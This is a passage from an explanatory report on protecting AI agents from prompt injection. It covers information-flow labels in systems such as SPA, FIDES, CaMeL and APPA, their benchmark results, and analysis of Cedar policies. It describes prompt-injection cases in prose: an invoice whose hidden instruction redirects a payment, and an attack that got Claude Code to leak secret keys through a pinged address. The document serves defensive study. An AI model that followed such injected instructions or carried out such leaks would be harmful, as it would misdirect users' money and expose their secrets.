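                      amount: details.amount)
```

Suppose the deployer has decided that invoices are secret and untrusted, since outsiders write them. The `pay` tool may receive secret data, but all its inputs must be trusted. SPA treats the user's request as trusted, and constants such as "Acme" take the request's label, which is public and trusted in this example. The checker works through the plan as follows:

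| Step | Combined input label | Result of the test | Label of the output |
|---|---|---|---|
| 1. `find_invoice` | Public, trusted | Passes | Secret, untrusted |
| 2. `q-llm` | Secret, untrusted | No test needed | Secret, untrusted |
| 3. `pay` | Secret, untrusted | Fails on integrity | None |

SPA rejects the plan before any tool runs, including `find_invoice`. The hidden instruction has no effect because the planning model never reads the invoice. Even so, without the integrity check, the plan would still have sent Michelle's money to the attacker while doing just what she asked.

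The checker rejects the plan without reading any account number, so it would reject the same plan for a legitimate invoice. If Michelle types the account number and the amount into her request, both are trusted and the checker allows the payment. If she types only the account number and the plan takes the amount from the invoice, the checker rejects the payment again, because one untrusted input makes the combined label untrusted.

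A branch can cause a rejection even when every input is a harmless constant. Suppose that instead of paying, the plan posts a notice on a public page if the invoice is large:

```text
3. condition details.amount > 1000
     then: tool post_notice("Finance is busy today")
     else: (no steps)
```

The notice's text is public and trusted, and it doesn't mention the invoice. But whether the notice appears depends on `details.amount`, which is secret and untrusted, so the program-counter label inside the branch is secret and untrusted too. If `post_notice` accepts only public, trusted inputs, the call fails both the confidentiality check and the integrity check. If the call went through, anyone who knew the plan could tell from the notice that Michelle had received an invoice for more than $1,000, and the attacker could make the notice appear by choosing a large amount.

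The checker must examine both branches because it runs before anyone knows the amount. The plan would fail in the same way if it posted the notice in the `else` branch instead.

SPA's language rules out Fenton's trick because a plan can't assign a new value to an existing variable, and variables created inside a branch disappear when the branch ends. A smaller leak remains because the interpreter stops the whole request if a tool fails. If a tool inside a secret branch fails, a later public notice that should appear in every case won't appear, and its absence suggests that the secret branch ran. Volpano and colleagues' theorem covers only runs that finish, and Girrens and Wang do not offer a corresponding proof for SPA.

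### From Monday to Tuesday

In the two-day version, Monday's request is only to find the invoice and keep its details. No step pays anyone, so the plan passes. SPA saves each result in three parts:

- the value, including the attacker's account number
- the label, which is secret and untrusted
- a description of the value's format and meaning, with a reference to the request that produced it.

On Tuesday Michelle asks the agent to "pay the invoice we discussed yesterday". The planning model sees only the descriptions of saved results. From these it can tell that Monday's `details` contains an account and an amount, so it writes a plan that retrieves and uses them:

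```text
1. details = retrieve(monday_invoice_details)
2. receipt = tool pay(account: details.account,
                      amount: details.amount)
```

The `retrieve` step restores the label along with the value, so the inputs to `pay` are again labeled secret and untrusted. The checker rejects the plan, as it would have on Monday.

The description and the label protect against different attacks. Showing the planning model a description instead of the saved invoice keeps the invoice's hidden instruction from changing Tuesday's plan. The label is needed because even a sensible plan could pay the attacker if SPA saved the account number without it. The description is safe to show because the planning model wrote its explanation of the value on Monday, before any tool had run.

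As in Meijer's email assistant, a poisoned tool description can still influence the plan, but the plan must then pass the flow check. SPA also has a mode that hides the installed tools during planning. In this mode, a model invents descriptions of the tools the request seems to need, the planner uses those descriptions, and SPA then matches them to real tools.

### Why a model's output keeps the label

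The plan's second step gave the invoice to an isolated model, and the output stayed secret and untrusted. In ordinary code, a checker can sometimes show that a result depends on only some of the inputs. If a function takes two letters and returns the length of the first, the checker can ignore the second letter's label. It can't do this for a language model, because any word in the input might affect any word in the output. The output therefore needs the combined label of all the model's input.

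Without this rule, a single model call could remove any restriction. A program could ask a model to summarise a secret contract and get most of its text back with a public label. An attacker could send an invoice that tells the model to report a particular account number, which the checker would then treat as trusted. Girrens and Wang call this laundering. Limiting the model's output to a fixed format doesn't prevent it, because an attacker's account number has the same format as a legitimate one.

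The rule severely restricts an ordinary agent, which adds each tool result to a single conversation. Once Michelle's assistant has read one email from a stranger, everything the model writes afterwards is untrusted, including its choice of the next tool. If `send_email` requires trusted input, the assistant can't use it for the rest of that conversation. This is another case of label creep, and it is worse with a language model because the model takes the whole conversation as input for every reply.

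Costa and colleagues mention a looser method by Siddiqui and others. It looks for the messages that influenced the model's reply and regenerates the reply from those messages alone, so the new reply needs only their labels. This can save a good deal of useful work, but the choice of which messages to keep depends on the full conversation, so it may still carry a little information from the messages left out.

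### Labels that travel with the run

FIDES and CaMeL hide data from the planning model to avoid tainting it. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) describes both as versions of the Dual LLM pattern, which the programmer Simon Willison proposed in 2023. In this pattern, one model plans and can call tools, and a separate model without tools reads untrusted text.

In FIDES, the planning model chooses one action at a time, as in an ordinary agent loop. Each tool labels its results, sometimes field by field, and FIDES keeps a label for the conversation so far. If a result would make that label more restrictive, FIDES stores the result in a variable and shows the model only the variable's name. Suppose the user asks for a summary of the latest three emails, sent as a message to a colleague:

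1. The model calls `read_emails`. FIDES stores the untrusted text and adds the name `#read_emails_0` to the conversation.
2. The model asks the isolated model to summarise that variable. FIDES stores the answer as `#query_llm_0`.
3. The model calls `send_message` with the colleague's name and `#query_llm_0`.
4. FIDES replaces the variable's name with its contents, checks the labels and sends the message.

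The model chose the tool and the recipient without reading the emails, so both are trusted. The message text is untrusted, but FIDES can still allow the call because its policies can set different requirements for each argument, whereas SPA applies one integrity requirement to all of a tool's inputs. For confidentiality, FIDES also checks that every recipient is allowed to read the message's contents. An attacker's email could still tell the isolated model to write an empty summary. Costa and colleagues note that a policy can prevent this by requiring the message text to be trusted too, but it would then block this task.

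Sometimes the planning model needs to know a variable's contents before choosing the next step. It can open the variable, which adds the contents and their label to the conversation, or ask the isolated model a question with a restricted answer, such as whether an email contains a meeting request. FIDES includes the answer's type in the answer's label, so a policy can treat a yes or no, which carries a single bit, less strictly than free text.

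In CaMeL, a planning model writes a whole program from the user's request, and a second model interprets untrusted content but cannot change the program. Girrens and Wang describe each value as carrying a record of where it came from and who may receive it. CaMeL calls these records capabilities, although they describe data and do not give their holder the right to perform an effect. When the program calls a tool, a policy written for that tool checks the records. For example, it might require that the recipient's address came from a trusted source. Such policies can express conditions that a simple ordering of labels cannot, but someone has to write each one correctly.

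### What a run reveals and what it misses

SPA's checker has one fixed label for everything that `find_invoice` might return, so if some invoices come from strangers, it has to treat all of them as untrusted. A runtime system can instead check the specific invoice returned. If it came from the company's own billing system, the tool can label it trusted and the payment can go ahead.

FIDES sets an email's confidentiality label at run time, because the label depends on the sender and recipients, who aren't known until the email arrives. The label records who may read the email. FIDES also checks only the path the agent takes, so a forbidden payment in a branch that never runs doesn't block the task.

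These labels protect the agent only if the rules assign them correctly. In one of Costa and colleagues' tests, the user asked the agent to change a password if it found a suspicious bank transaction. FIDES hid the payment's subject line, which was untrusted, but treated the amount as trusted. The agent flagged the amount as suspicious and changed the password, which the policy allowed. But whoever makes a payment usually chooses the amount as well as the subject line, so an attacker might be able to trigger the password change by sending a large payment.

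A runtime system has no information about the paths the agent did not take. Costa and colleagues prove that FIDES can enforce explicit secrecy, a weaker property than noninterference. Under explicit secrecy, changing the secret data does not change the public results of any fixed sequence of actions. The secret data may still affect which sequence the agent chooses, so someone who sees which tools ran can learn something about that data.

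Suppose Michelle's assistant reads her private calendar and, if she has a medical appointment, calls `set_away()`, a tool that changes her public status. The call has no arguments, so a check on arguments finds nothing wrong, but her colleagues can still see that her status changed. In SPA, if the equivalent plan made this decision in a `condition` step, the branch would have a secret program-counter label. The check would then reject the call if `set_away` accepted only public inputs.

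Costa and colleagues argue that full noninterference would be too restrictive for this kind of agent, because after reading anything secret it could hardly use any tool with a publicly visible effect. They think explicit secrecy, combined with safety rules about which actions the agent may take, is enough to stop most practical prompt injections. Secrecy rules alone are not enough, because untrusted text can still influence which tools the agent calls. Their claim about the combination is plausible as long as the planning model has read no untrusted text, because an attacker then has no direct way to make it signal secrets through its choice of tools. It is weaker if the planning model itself is hostile.

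FIDES can also halt an agent partway through a task, for example by blocking a hotel payment after the agent has booked the flight, whereas SPA would reject the whole plan before the agent booked anything. Denning noticed that blocked actions can also leak information. A program with access to a secret number could be written to break a rule that many times, and anyone who could read the log of violations would learn the number.

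### Checking before and after a call

Some systems check a tool's declared label before a call and its actual result afterwards. *APPA* (Kravchenko, Liventsev and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a tool, `share_legal_packet`, that reads a confidential financial ledger and emails it to someone in a single call. Before the call, the agent has read nothing secret, so a check on the agent's current label would let the call through. The result would come back labelled secret only after the email had been sent.

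APPA therefore uses the tool's declaration to work out what the label would be after the call, and checks the recipient against that label. If the recipient may not read financial data, APPA blocks the call before the tool reads or sends anything. Because outside services do not always behave as declared, APPA also checks the actual result before adding it to the conversation. This second check can keep an unexpected result away from the model, but it can't recall an email that a wrongly declared tool has already sent.

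Many existing tools declare no labels. APPA marks their results as unknown and lets the agent continue until an action, such as sending the data to a customer, depends on the missing label. A component that the operator trusts must then supply a label within limits set in advance. If none can, APPA blocks the action.

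## How much useful work does strict flow checking block?

Suppose Michelle asks her assistant to confirm that a colleague's file exists in the personnel system, and then to send the whole company a routine notice whose wording she supplies. The notice contains nothing from the file, but a strict flow checker will block it because, after the lookup, the file's restrictions cover everything the assistant's model writes. This problem is called label creep. Kravchenko and colleagues use a task like this to test APPA, their system for checking labels before and after each call.

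In APPA, as in FIDES, reading an item can remove permitted readers or lower the conversation's trust level, but it can never add readers or raise the trust level. Kravchenko and colleagues prove that if a call fails because a recipient is not a permitted reader or the trust level is too low, the agent cannot unblock it by reading more.

People use agents largely to act on outside information, for example to pay an invoice or work through a to-do list that arrived by email. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) notes that users often give agents incomplete instructions and expect them to find the rest along the way. A rule that untrusted data may not influence important actions blocks such work even when there is no attacker.

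### Dividing the work among agents

Giving different tools to different agents, so that only one of them sees the personnel file, can slow the spread of labels. *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems* (Gregory, Domico and colleagues, 2026) simulated such arrangements without running a language model. Each task was a random network of up to 20 tool calls, some of which returned sensitive data. An agent acquired a sensitive label when it called one of these tools or passed on a message containing the result, and it never lost the label. The share of calls with a sensitive label served as a proxy for lost usefulness.

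If every message goes through a central coordinator, the coordinator soon picks up the label and spreads it to the other agents. With five agents and four sensitive calls out of 20, this layout did about five percentage points worse than the ideal, while a layout where all agents could contact each other directly matched the ideal. Concentrating the sensitive tools in a few agents also helped. So did adding agents, though the number of connections to monitor could then grow with the square of the number of agents.

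No layout stopped the labels from spreading, and Gregory and colleagues conclude that agents also need a way to remove them. The labels kept spreading partly because the simulation has no mechanism for removing them. The simulation also can't measure how many real tasks would fail, since a policy may allow many calls that carry a sensitive label.

### SPA with and without its checks

Girrens and Wang measured how much useful work is lost with SPA, which checks a complete plan before any tool runs. They used AgentDojo's 949 attack trials and its 97 tasks, which cover office work, Slack messages, travel and banking. They also built AgentDojo-MQ, which splits each task into two to five requests so that the agent has to reuse earlier results. The model was gpt-5.4-nano, a small model. Results are given as percentages.

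| Benchmark | Flow checks | Tasks completed, no attack | Tasks completed under attack | Successful attacks |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo | Off | 53.0 | 54.7 | 0.4 |
| AgentDojo | On | 29.0 | 29.5 | 0.0 |
| AgentDojo-MQ | Off | 62.5 | 60.0 | 0.3 |
| AgentDojo-MQ | On | 35.3 | 33.7 | 0.2 |

These averages give more weight to groups of tasks with more attack trials. If each task counts once, the checks cut completed AgentDojo tasks from 51 to 27.

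SPA fixes its plan before reading any outside text, so even with the checks off, only four of the 949 attacks succeeded. All four involved the same banking task, in which the isolated model read hostile text and the plan passed its output to a tool that should accept only trusted data. Three led to unauthorised transfers and one to a changed password. The 0.2% on AgentDojo-MQ comes from two trials that AgentDojo scored as successful attacks even though SPA had rejected the plan.

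Most of the lost tasks failed the integrity check. About 81% of AgentDojo trials ran the plan with the checks off, but only 37% did with them on. SPA rejected about 53%, usually because the plan passed one tool's untrusted output to another tool that required trusted input. On AgentDojo-MQ, it rejected about 45%. SPA has no way for a user to vouch for untrusted output.

Completion fell by 35 percentage points on travel tasks, 28.6 on Slack, 25 on office work and 6.25 on banking. The banking figure may understate the loss, because five of the 16 banking tasks pass AgentDojo's test even if the agent does nothing.

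### FIDES and CaMeL on the same tasks

Costa and colleagues tested FIDES, which hides untrusted text from the planning model, on AgentDojo with GPT-4o. They compared it with an ordinary agent whose conversation takes on the labels of everything it reads. The table gives the percentage of tasks each agent completed when there was no attack.

| Tasks | Ordinary agent, checks off | Ordinary agent, checks on | FIDES, checks off | FIDES, checks on |
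|---|---|---|---|---|
| Office work | 75.0 | 37.0 | 63.5 | 59.0 |
| Travel | 70.0 | 73.0 | 50.0 | 41.0 |
| Banking | 98.8 | 37.5 | 65.0 | 52.5 |
| Slack | 93.3 | 20.0 | 63.8 | 47.6 |
| Average of the four | 84.3 | 41.9 | 60.6 | 50.0 |

The checks halved the ordinary agent's average but lowered FIDES's by only about 11 points. Even with the checks off, FIDES trailed the ordinary agent by 24 points, because GPT-4o often mishandled the variables that hide untrusted text. With the stronger reasoning model o1, that gap shrank to 6.3 points. Better models can therefore recover some of the loss, but they can't complete a task that the policy forbids.

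After correcting for cases that AgentDojo misjudged, Costa and colleagues counted 152 successful attacks on the ordinary agent and 21 on FIDES with the checks off, and none on either with the checks on. However, they labelled a data field untrusted if at least one AgentDojo attack targeted it, and operators of real systems don't know in advance which fields attackers will use.

Odersky and colleagues compared TACIT's attack trials with CaMeL's. In its trials, CaMeL completed 76.1% of tasks with o4-mini-high and 45.3% with Gemini 2.5 Pro, and one attack succeeded in total. Under attack, FIDES completed an average of 50.2% of tasks across the four task groups, and SPA completed 29.5%.

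These figures can't be used to rank the three systems, because the models and policies differed. Changing only the model shifted CaMeL's score by 31 points, and SPA used a small model that completed just 53% of tasks even without flow checks. Policies also affect attack rates. When Kravchenko and colleagues set up two versions of FIDES for their own benchmark, attacks succeeded in 26% to 35% of runs because the policies they gave it lacked some rules the tasks needed, such as one specifying exactly who could receive a document.

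### Deliberate exceptions

Declassification makes a secret value less secret, and endorsement makes an untrusted value trusted. Michelle declassifies a summary of a confidential report when she clears it for a client, and she endorses an account number when she confirms that it belongs to Acme. Both are exceptions to noninterference, because something the client sees then depends on a secret, and a stranger's text influences a payment.

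A policy can still restrict how these exceptions happen. *Agent libOS* (2026) describes a way to classify declassification rules by what information they release, who may release it, and where and when. FIDES can let a confidential document go to an outsider if the planning model had read nothing untrusted when it decided to send it. This is a form of robust declassification, in which an attacker can't trigger the release, although a model that misunderstands Michelle's request still can.

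*The LLMbda Calculus* (2026), which defines a formal language for agents, applies the same idea to endorsement. Its `endorse` operation raises a value's trust but leaves its secrecy unchanged. If untrusted data determined whether the program reached the operation, the result stays untrusted. So if an attacker's email causes the program to take a branch that endorses the account number in the email, the number stays untrusted.

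Software could also make these decisions. Costa and colleagues suggest that a system might mark a document as trusted after a prompt-injection detector clears it. This would save people work, but any attack that fooled the detector would count as trusted data. *Agent libOS*, however, lets such a classifier block an action or refer it for review, but not approve it.

### Asking the user

A user can either approve a blocked call or endorse the data behind it. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* presents Prudentia, an extension of FIDES that can ask for either. If an email lists ten tasks, approving each action takes ten prompts, but endorsing the email takes one. The single prompt is riskier because the agent then trusts the whole email. If the user overlooks an eleventh task that an attacker added, the integrity check will not catch it. Prudentia has no equivalent option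 for declassifying data, because its designers think that whether to release private information depends too much on the situation.

The paper puts the loss reported for systems such as FIDES and CaMeL at up to 30% on AgentDojo, but argues that the usual comparison is unfair. It sets a protected agent working alone against an unprotected one that may take any action, whereas many real products ask the user before important actions. The paper therefore measured how many tasks each agent could complete without any approvals. With o3-mini as the model, the results were:

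| Agent | Tasks completed without approvals (%) |
|---|---|
| Ordinary agent that must ask before every important action | 24.3 |
| Ordinary agent with flow checks | 35.5 |
| FIDES | 50.1 |
| Prudentia | 59.1 |

By this measure, flow checks let an agent do more on its own, because it has to ask the user only when a call breaks the policy. This is a good argument for adding them to products that now ask before every important action. It doesn't apply to agents that users already let work unattended, because each blocked call is a new interruption.

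The paper assumes that users reject every harmful call, which is optimistic if they see many prompts. The system also has to ask before each harmful call. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* describes an attack on Claude Code, which asked for approval before many commands that could send data out but mistakenly exempted `ping`. Instructions hidden in a code file led the agent to read secret keys and include them in an address it pinged. The keys reached the attacker when the computer looked up that address.

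### Short answers and finer labels

The restricted answers that FIDES can show its planning model also weaken the guarantee, because they let untrusted text have a small influence on the model instead of none. An answer with *k* possible values carries at most log₂ *k* bits, so a choice among eight options carries at most three, which is too little to hold an instruction. But even one bit can do a lot of damage if it decides whether to make a payment. Short answers also add up, and 40 yes-or-no answers can encode five ordinary characters.

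Finer labels can let more tasks finish without weakening the guarantee, provided the labels are correct. Girrens and Wang suggest that future systems label individual fields and check each argument separately, as FIDES already can. For example, a mail server can often verify a sender's address, so the address could be trusted even when the message isn't. But someone has to decide which fields an outsider can control, and a wrong decision could let an attack through.

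### Recovering from a blocked call

When APPA blocks a call, it tells the agent which steps could make the call acceptable. The main options are:

- **Complete a missing step.** The policy might require a record of legal clearance before the agent emails contract terms.
- **Get a ruling.** An authority that the operator has chosen can approve this exact call. The authority can be a person, a fixed rule or another model. The ruling changes no labels and doesn't cover later calls.
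- **Clean the data.** Trusted code can remove personal details, for example, and give the result a less restrictive label.
- **Use a branch.** The agent can do the restricted reading in a temporary copy of the conversation.

A branch would solve the problem with Michelle's company notice:

1. The agent opens a branch, which starts with the main conversation's text and label.
2. The branch reads the personnel file, and only the branch's label becomes more restrictive.
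3. The branch returns an answer in a format that the main agent fixed beforehand, such as yes or no.
4. APPA checks the format and discards the rest of the branch.
5. If the operator's policy allows the answer to carry a less restrictive label, the main conversation keeps its original label and the agent can send the notice.

The format check doesn't verify that the answer is true. If a branch reads hostile text, an attacker may be able to choose any answer the format allows. Discarding a branch also doesn't undo actions it has already taken, such as sending an email.

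Kravchenko and colleagues tested APPA with three models on Bench-Corp, a set of 20 office tasks they designed. In half the runs, an extra prompt encouraged the model to follow instructions it found in documents. APPA completed the task in 535 of 600 runs (89%), and no attacks succeeded. An unguarded version completed the task in 546 runs (91%), but attacks succeeded in 197 (33%).

The recovery options accounted for much of this result. With GPT-5.6 Luna, the full system completed 88% of runs. That fell to 56.5% without branches, and to 35% when the agent couldn't carry out the remedies APPA suggests. No attacks succeeded in either case, so removing recovery made the agent much less useful without making it measurably safer.

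Bench-Corp probably overstates APPA's performance, because its tasks were built around APPA's mechanisms. On AgentThreatBench, an existing benchmark, APPA completed 510 of 720 runs (71%) with no successful attacks. An unprotected agent completed 648 (90%), but attacks succeeded in 235 of the 720 runs (33%). Part of the completion gap comes from three tasks whose scoring requires an exact phrase that APPA's fixed-format answers often lacked.

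The researchers left out AgentDojo partly because newer models resist its attacks without added defences. GPT-5.6 Luna followed none of the injected instructions in 160 unprotected runs, compared with 31% for GPT-4o. A low attack success rate on AgentDojo is therefore weak evidence that a defence works if it was tested with a recent model.

APPA guarantees that a call can break a flow rule only with a recorded ruling, within limits the operator set in advance. It doesn't guarantee noninterference. If the authority is a language model, it may approve a call it should have refused.

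### Risky tasks or coarse labels?

Some of the blocked tasks are dangerous. In AgentDojo's banking task 12, the agent has to read a file and schedule a payment based on its contents. If the agent pays whatever account is listed in the file, anyone who can edit the file can redirect the money. FIDES blocks this task, and Costa and colleagues consider that the intended result. The four attacks that succeeded against SPA without flow checks all used this task.

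The travel tasks suggest that labels and policies can also be too coarse. SPA's checks lower its score there by 35 points, but Costa and colleagues' checks did not lower the ordinary agent's score, because their policy let many travel tools act on untrusted data as long as no private data leaked. Their policy accepts some risk, since hostile text could still change what the agent tells the user. Still, much of SPA's loss on travel probably comes from its stricter policy rather than from the tasks themselves.

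Costa and colleagues' classification of the tasks gives a rough idea of how many are risky. In about 20 of the 97, the agent can't know which actions to take until it has read the data. In the rest, the user's request determines the actions, although some of these tasks still take a detail such as an account number from an untrusted source. More than 20 tasks are therefore risky, but SPA's rejection of about half of all trials still looks excessive. It makes sense for a person to confirm the account number in task 12, but Michelle's company notice should need no approval.

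## What can be proved about a policy written as code before it is deployed?

Capability and label systems enforce whatever rules an operator gives them, including bad ones. FIDES let attacks through in Kravchenko and colleagues' tests because its policies lacked necessary rules. Such gaps are hard to spot when every tool's code contains its own checks. Policy-as-code moves the checks out of the program and into a formal language, where a security team can read them all in one place and software can search them for mistakes before any agent depends on them.

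### A gate in front of the tool

A policy engine sits between the agent and its tools. It receives each call and answers "allow" or "deny" before the tool runs. Here is a rule for a refund tool in Cedar, a policy language from Amazon Web Services (AWS), adapted from an example in AWS's *Understanding Cedar policies*:

```text
permit (
  principal is AgentCore::OAuthUser,
  action == AgentCore::Action::"RefundTool__process_refund",
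  resource
)
when { context.input.amount <= 500 };
```

The principal is the user or program making the request, the action is the tool, and the resource is the gateway the call passes through. The context holds the tool's arguments. This rule lets any signed-in user's agent refund up to $500 per call. If the agent requests a $620 refund, the condition is false and no other rule permits the call, so Cedar denies it by default. Cedar also has `forbid` rules, which override every `permit`, and the order of the rules never affects the decision.

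Some of the engine's inputs are more trustworthy than others. AWS's *Why Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore chose Cedar for securing agentic workflows* notes that a customer's tier can come from a signed login token, which the model cannot alter, whereas the order quantity comes from the model's call. A limit on the refund amount still works even though the model supplies the amount, because the tool receives the same number that the engine checked. A condition such as `context.input.managerApproved == true` would be worthless, because a hijacked model could write `true`.

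Analysing a policy's rules before deployment can settle a question about every call they could ever receive, such as whether any refund above $500 can get through. Evaluating the rules at runtime decides only the current call, so even a million correctly handled refunds would not settle that question.

### Cedar and Rego

The main alternative to Cedar is Open Policy Agent (OPA), whose policies use a language called Rego. *VeriWeave Govern* (Mohsenzadegan, Tavakkoli and Kyamakya, 2026) describes OPA as a tool for general-purpose policy evaluation and Cedar as a safe and analysable language for authorization. A Rego rule can loop over a list, filter it and add up the results. It can also match regular expressions, call functions that the policy's author defined, and fetch a web page during evaluation.

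Cedar has none of these features. It leaves out loops and anything that changes state, and AWS's *Limitations* adds that it has no floating-point numbers and no pattern matching beyond a `*` wildcard. As a result, evaluating a Cedar policy always finishes quickly, and software can translate the policy into a logical formula of fixed size. A similar translation for all of Rego would be much harder, because a solver would have to reason about lists of any length and any possible reply from a web server. An organisation whose rules need those features may reasonably choose Rego, but it will have to rely more on tests.

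### From a policy to a formula

The simplest check compares a policy with a schema. Amazon's agent platform, Bedrock AgentCore, generates the schema from the descriptions that MCP servers publish for their tools. According to AWS's *Schema constraints*, each tool becomes an action, and each of its arguments gets a Cedar type. A policy fails validation if it misspells the refund tool's name, mentions an argument the tool lacks, or compares an amount with text.

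A valid policy can still allow the wrong calls, and finding those takes a solver. Cedar's symbolic compiler translates the rules into formulas for an SMT solver, a program that searches for values satisfying a set of logical and arithmetical constraints. For a request *r*, the translation follows Cedar's own definition:

> *Allowed*(*r*) = (some `permit` matches *r*) and not (some `forbid` matches *r*)

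To prove that the refund policy respects its limit, the analyser uses the solver to search for a refund request *r* with *Allowed*(*r*) and *amount*(*r*) > 500. If the policy allows such a request, the solver returns an example. If the solver proves that none exists, the limit holds for every amount and every user.

The same method compares two policies. The analyser searches for a request that policy *A* allows and policy *B* denies. If none exists, *A* is at most as permissive as *B*. If there is also no request that *B* allows and *A* denies, the two policies are equivalent, even if they are written differently.

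AWS gives examples of mistakes that this analysis finds:

- **A contradiction.** A rule permits refunds for customers whose tier equals "Gold" and also equals "Platinum". Nobody has both tiers, so the rule permits nothing. The author meant "or".
- **A condition that is always true.** A rule permits bulk discounts if the quantity is at least 100, or below 100. Every order qualifies.
- **A conflict.** One rule permits gold customers' refunds under $100, while another forbids gold and platinum customers' refunds under $500. The `forbid` wins, so the `permit` never has any effect.

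An edit can also widen access while appearing to narrow it. In another of AWS's examples, a rule permits discounts on orders of 50 items or more unless the order includes limited-edition products. Someone changes the exception to read "limited edition and more than 200 items". The added condition narrows the exception, so the rule now permits more discounts. An order for 73 limited-edition items, for example, used to be refused the discount and now gets it. The analyser reports that the new version is "more permissive" for discounts and equivalent for refunds. A reviewer who sees that report can decide whether the company wants to discount those orders without working out the logic of the edit.

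### Proofs about Cedar itself

These results depend on Cedar working as its definition says. AWS's *Introducing Cedar, an open-source language for access control* (2023) reports that the company's engineers wrote a formal model of the authorization engine and related tools, then proved safety and correctness properties of the model. These include basic rules of the language, such as that the engine allows no request without a matching `permit` and that a matching `forbid` always wins. Customers run a separate engine written in Rust, and AWS tests that it agrees with the model. The proofs cover only the model, so a bug that the tests never trigger could still make the Rust engine give a different answer.

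Validation still leaves a few runtime errors possible. Cedar's whole numbers have a fixed size, so adding two very large ones fails. When a rule fails, the engine skips it and decides from the remaining rules. Skipping a `permit` is harmless, but a `forbid` might add a fee to a refund and compare the sum with a limit. An enormous refund could then cause an error, and the engine would skip the rule that should have blocked it. An analyser can rule this out by using the solver to check that no request causes an error.

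### AgentCore Policy as it now stands

Amazon made its policy service for agents generally available in March 2026, according to AWS's *Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore is now generally available* (2026). An operator creates a policy engine, adds rules to it and attaches it to a gateway, which submits every tool call it receives to the engine. The rules are outside the agent's code, so a security team can change them without modifying the agent. They cover only the calls that go through the gateway.

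When an operator attaches policies to a gateway, the service uses Cedar's analysis to check the whole set together and refuses the operation if it finds logical errors such as conflicts. When an agent requests the list of available tools, the gateway uses the analysis to omit any tool that the policies would deny regardless of the arguments. This makes the model less likely to call those tools, and the engine would refuse the calls anyway.

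Operators can weaken these checks. AWS's documentation on testing policies shows a setting that ignores all validation findings, and a `LOG_ONLY` mode that records a policy's decisions without enforcing them. This mode is useful for trying a new rule on real traffic, but the rule will not block anything if the operator forgets to switch to `ENFORCE`. AWS also warns that a gateway without permission to consult its engine denies every tool call, including those the policies permit.

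The service now supports more than plain Cedar. According to AWS's *Policy in Amazon Bedrock AgentCore*, a policy can also depend on earlier events in the session and on scores from Guardrails, a service that rates content for problems such as prompt attacks. The engine applies a score threshold the same way every time, but the score is a classifier's estimate, so no analysis of the policy can show that the classifier will recognise an attack.

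### A generator and two critics

Most organisations write their rules in ordinary prose, which a language model can translate into code. In AgentCore, a model drafts a Cedar policy from an administrator's description. The validator then checks the draft against the tool schema, and the solver checks for rules that allow everything, deny everything or contain impossible conditions. The service returns any errors to the model for correction.

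*Autoformalization of Agent Instructions into Policy-as-Code* (Mondl, Maisel and Brock, 2026) adds a second kind of review. Gemini 3 Pro writes Cedar rules from the agent's instructions, its tool descriptions and the organisation's policy documents. A "hard critic" runs Cedar's own tools to find syntax errors, schema violations, contradictions and rules that have no effect. A "soft critic", made of two calls to a smaller model, checks whether the rules match the meaning of the original text. Gemini 3 Pro then revises the rules in response to both critics.

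Mondl and colleagues tested the rules on MedAgentBench, in which an agent works with electronic medical records. Hong and colleagues had earlier written an 88-rule policy for it and programmed 23 of the rules by hand. Mondl and colleagues translated the whole policy, had another model add constraints from Hong and colleagues' code, and replayed recorded agent runs through the Cedar engine.

| Tasks | Tools in the recorded run | Runs blocked | Blocked among runs that tried to change a record |
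|---|---|---|---|
| Ordinary | Raw web requests | 91 of 300 | 89 of 89 |
| Ordinary | Typed tools | 173 of 300 | 79 of 84 |
| Ordinary | Typed tools with the 23 rules | 167 of 300 | 85 of 86 |
| Adversarial | Raw web requests | 36 of 50 | 34 of 34 |
| Adversarial | Typed tools | 41 of 50 | 33 of 33 |
| Adversarial | Typed tools with the 23 rules | 42 of 49 | 32 of 32 |

The high block rates may mean, as Mondl and colleagues argue, that their rules cover more of the policy than the hand-written ones, but a single rule forbidding all changes would have scored 100% in the last column. The engine blocked 253 of the 259 ordinary, unattacked runs that tried to change a record. With typed tools, it also blocked 94 ordinary runs that only read data.

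Two rules, each of which fired 416 times, explain part of this. They require the agent to restate the patient's identity and to get confirmation before any change. The recorded agents apparently hadn't done so, and they couldn't respond to a refusal in a replay. A live agent might have asked for confirmation and then finished the task. The experiment measures coverage, as its designers acknowledge. It doesn't measure how much useful work agents could still do under the rules or how accurate the translation is.

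### Valid, but not what anyone asked for

Amazon's original version of the refund policy has a small mistake in its limit. The requirement in AWS's documentation reads "$500 or less", but the code beneath it tests `context.input.amount < 500`, which rejects a refund of exactly $500. The code is valid Cedar, contradicts nothing and permits a sensible set of requests, so none of the generic checks would catch the error. Units can cause a bigger error. If the refund tool counts in cents, a limit of 500 means $5.

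Zhou, Vatsa and Eiers (2026), in *RAISE*, give an example where the mistake grants too much. A company allows its finance managers to pay invoices during business hours only. Each invoice also needs approval, except when the manager is on the corporate network. The network exception is meant to lift just the approval requirement:

> manager and business hours and (approved or on network)

A natural way to write it in Cedar is as a separate `permit` for managers on the network, which gives a different result:

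> (manager and business hours and approved) or (manager and on network)

Under the faulty version, a manager in the office at midnight can pay an unapproved invoice. A solver finds that case at once if someone gives it the correct formula to compare against. Without that formula, it cannot determine which version is correct.

Strong models make such mistakes often. Zhou and colleagues gave GPT-6 Astra and Claude Opus 5 one attempt to write a policy for each of 375 requirements. Over 97% of the policies were valid, but only 33.6% of GPT-6 Astra's and 30.7% of Claude Opus 5's passed every check of what the policy had to allow and deny. A small open model that the researchers trained on verified examples reached 46.9%. Some of the failures may be due to incorrect checks, because another system, AutoCedar, generated them and it sometimes misinterprets requirements too.

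### Approving the target first

AutoCedar addresses the missing comparison by building one before it writes the policy. Vatsa, Shome and colleagues (2026), in *AUTOCEDAR*, explain it with a musician's app. Band members and the producer may download tracks, but no one may download a track under embargo. The system works in five steps:

1. A model proposes the vocabulary, such as "track" and "under embargo", one declaration at a time. A reviewer, either a person or another model, approves or rejects each.
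2. The model writes each sentence of the requirements as one small Cedar condition, which the reviewer also has to approve.
3. Ordinary code combines the approved conditions into floors, which are requests the final policy must allow, and ceilings, which bound what it may allow.
4. A model writes the complete policy.
5. The solver checks that the policy contains every floor, stays under every ceiling and never causes a runtime error. If a check fails, the model learns whether to loosen or tighten the policy and usually gets a request that shows the fault. It can change the policy but not the target.

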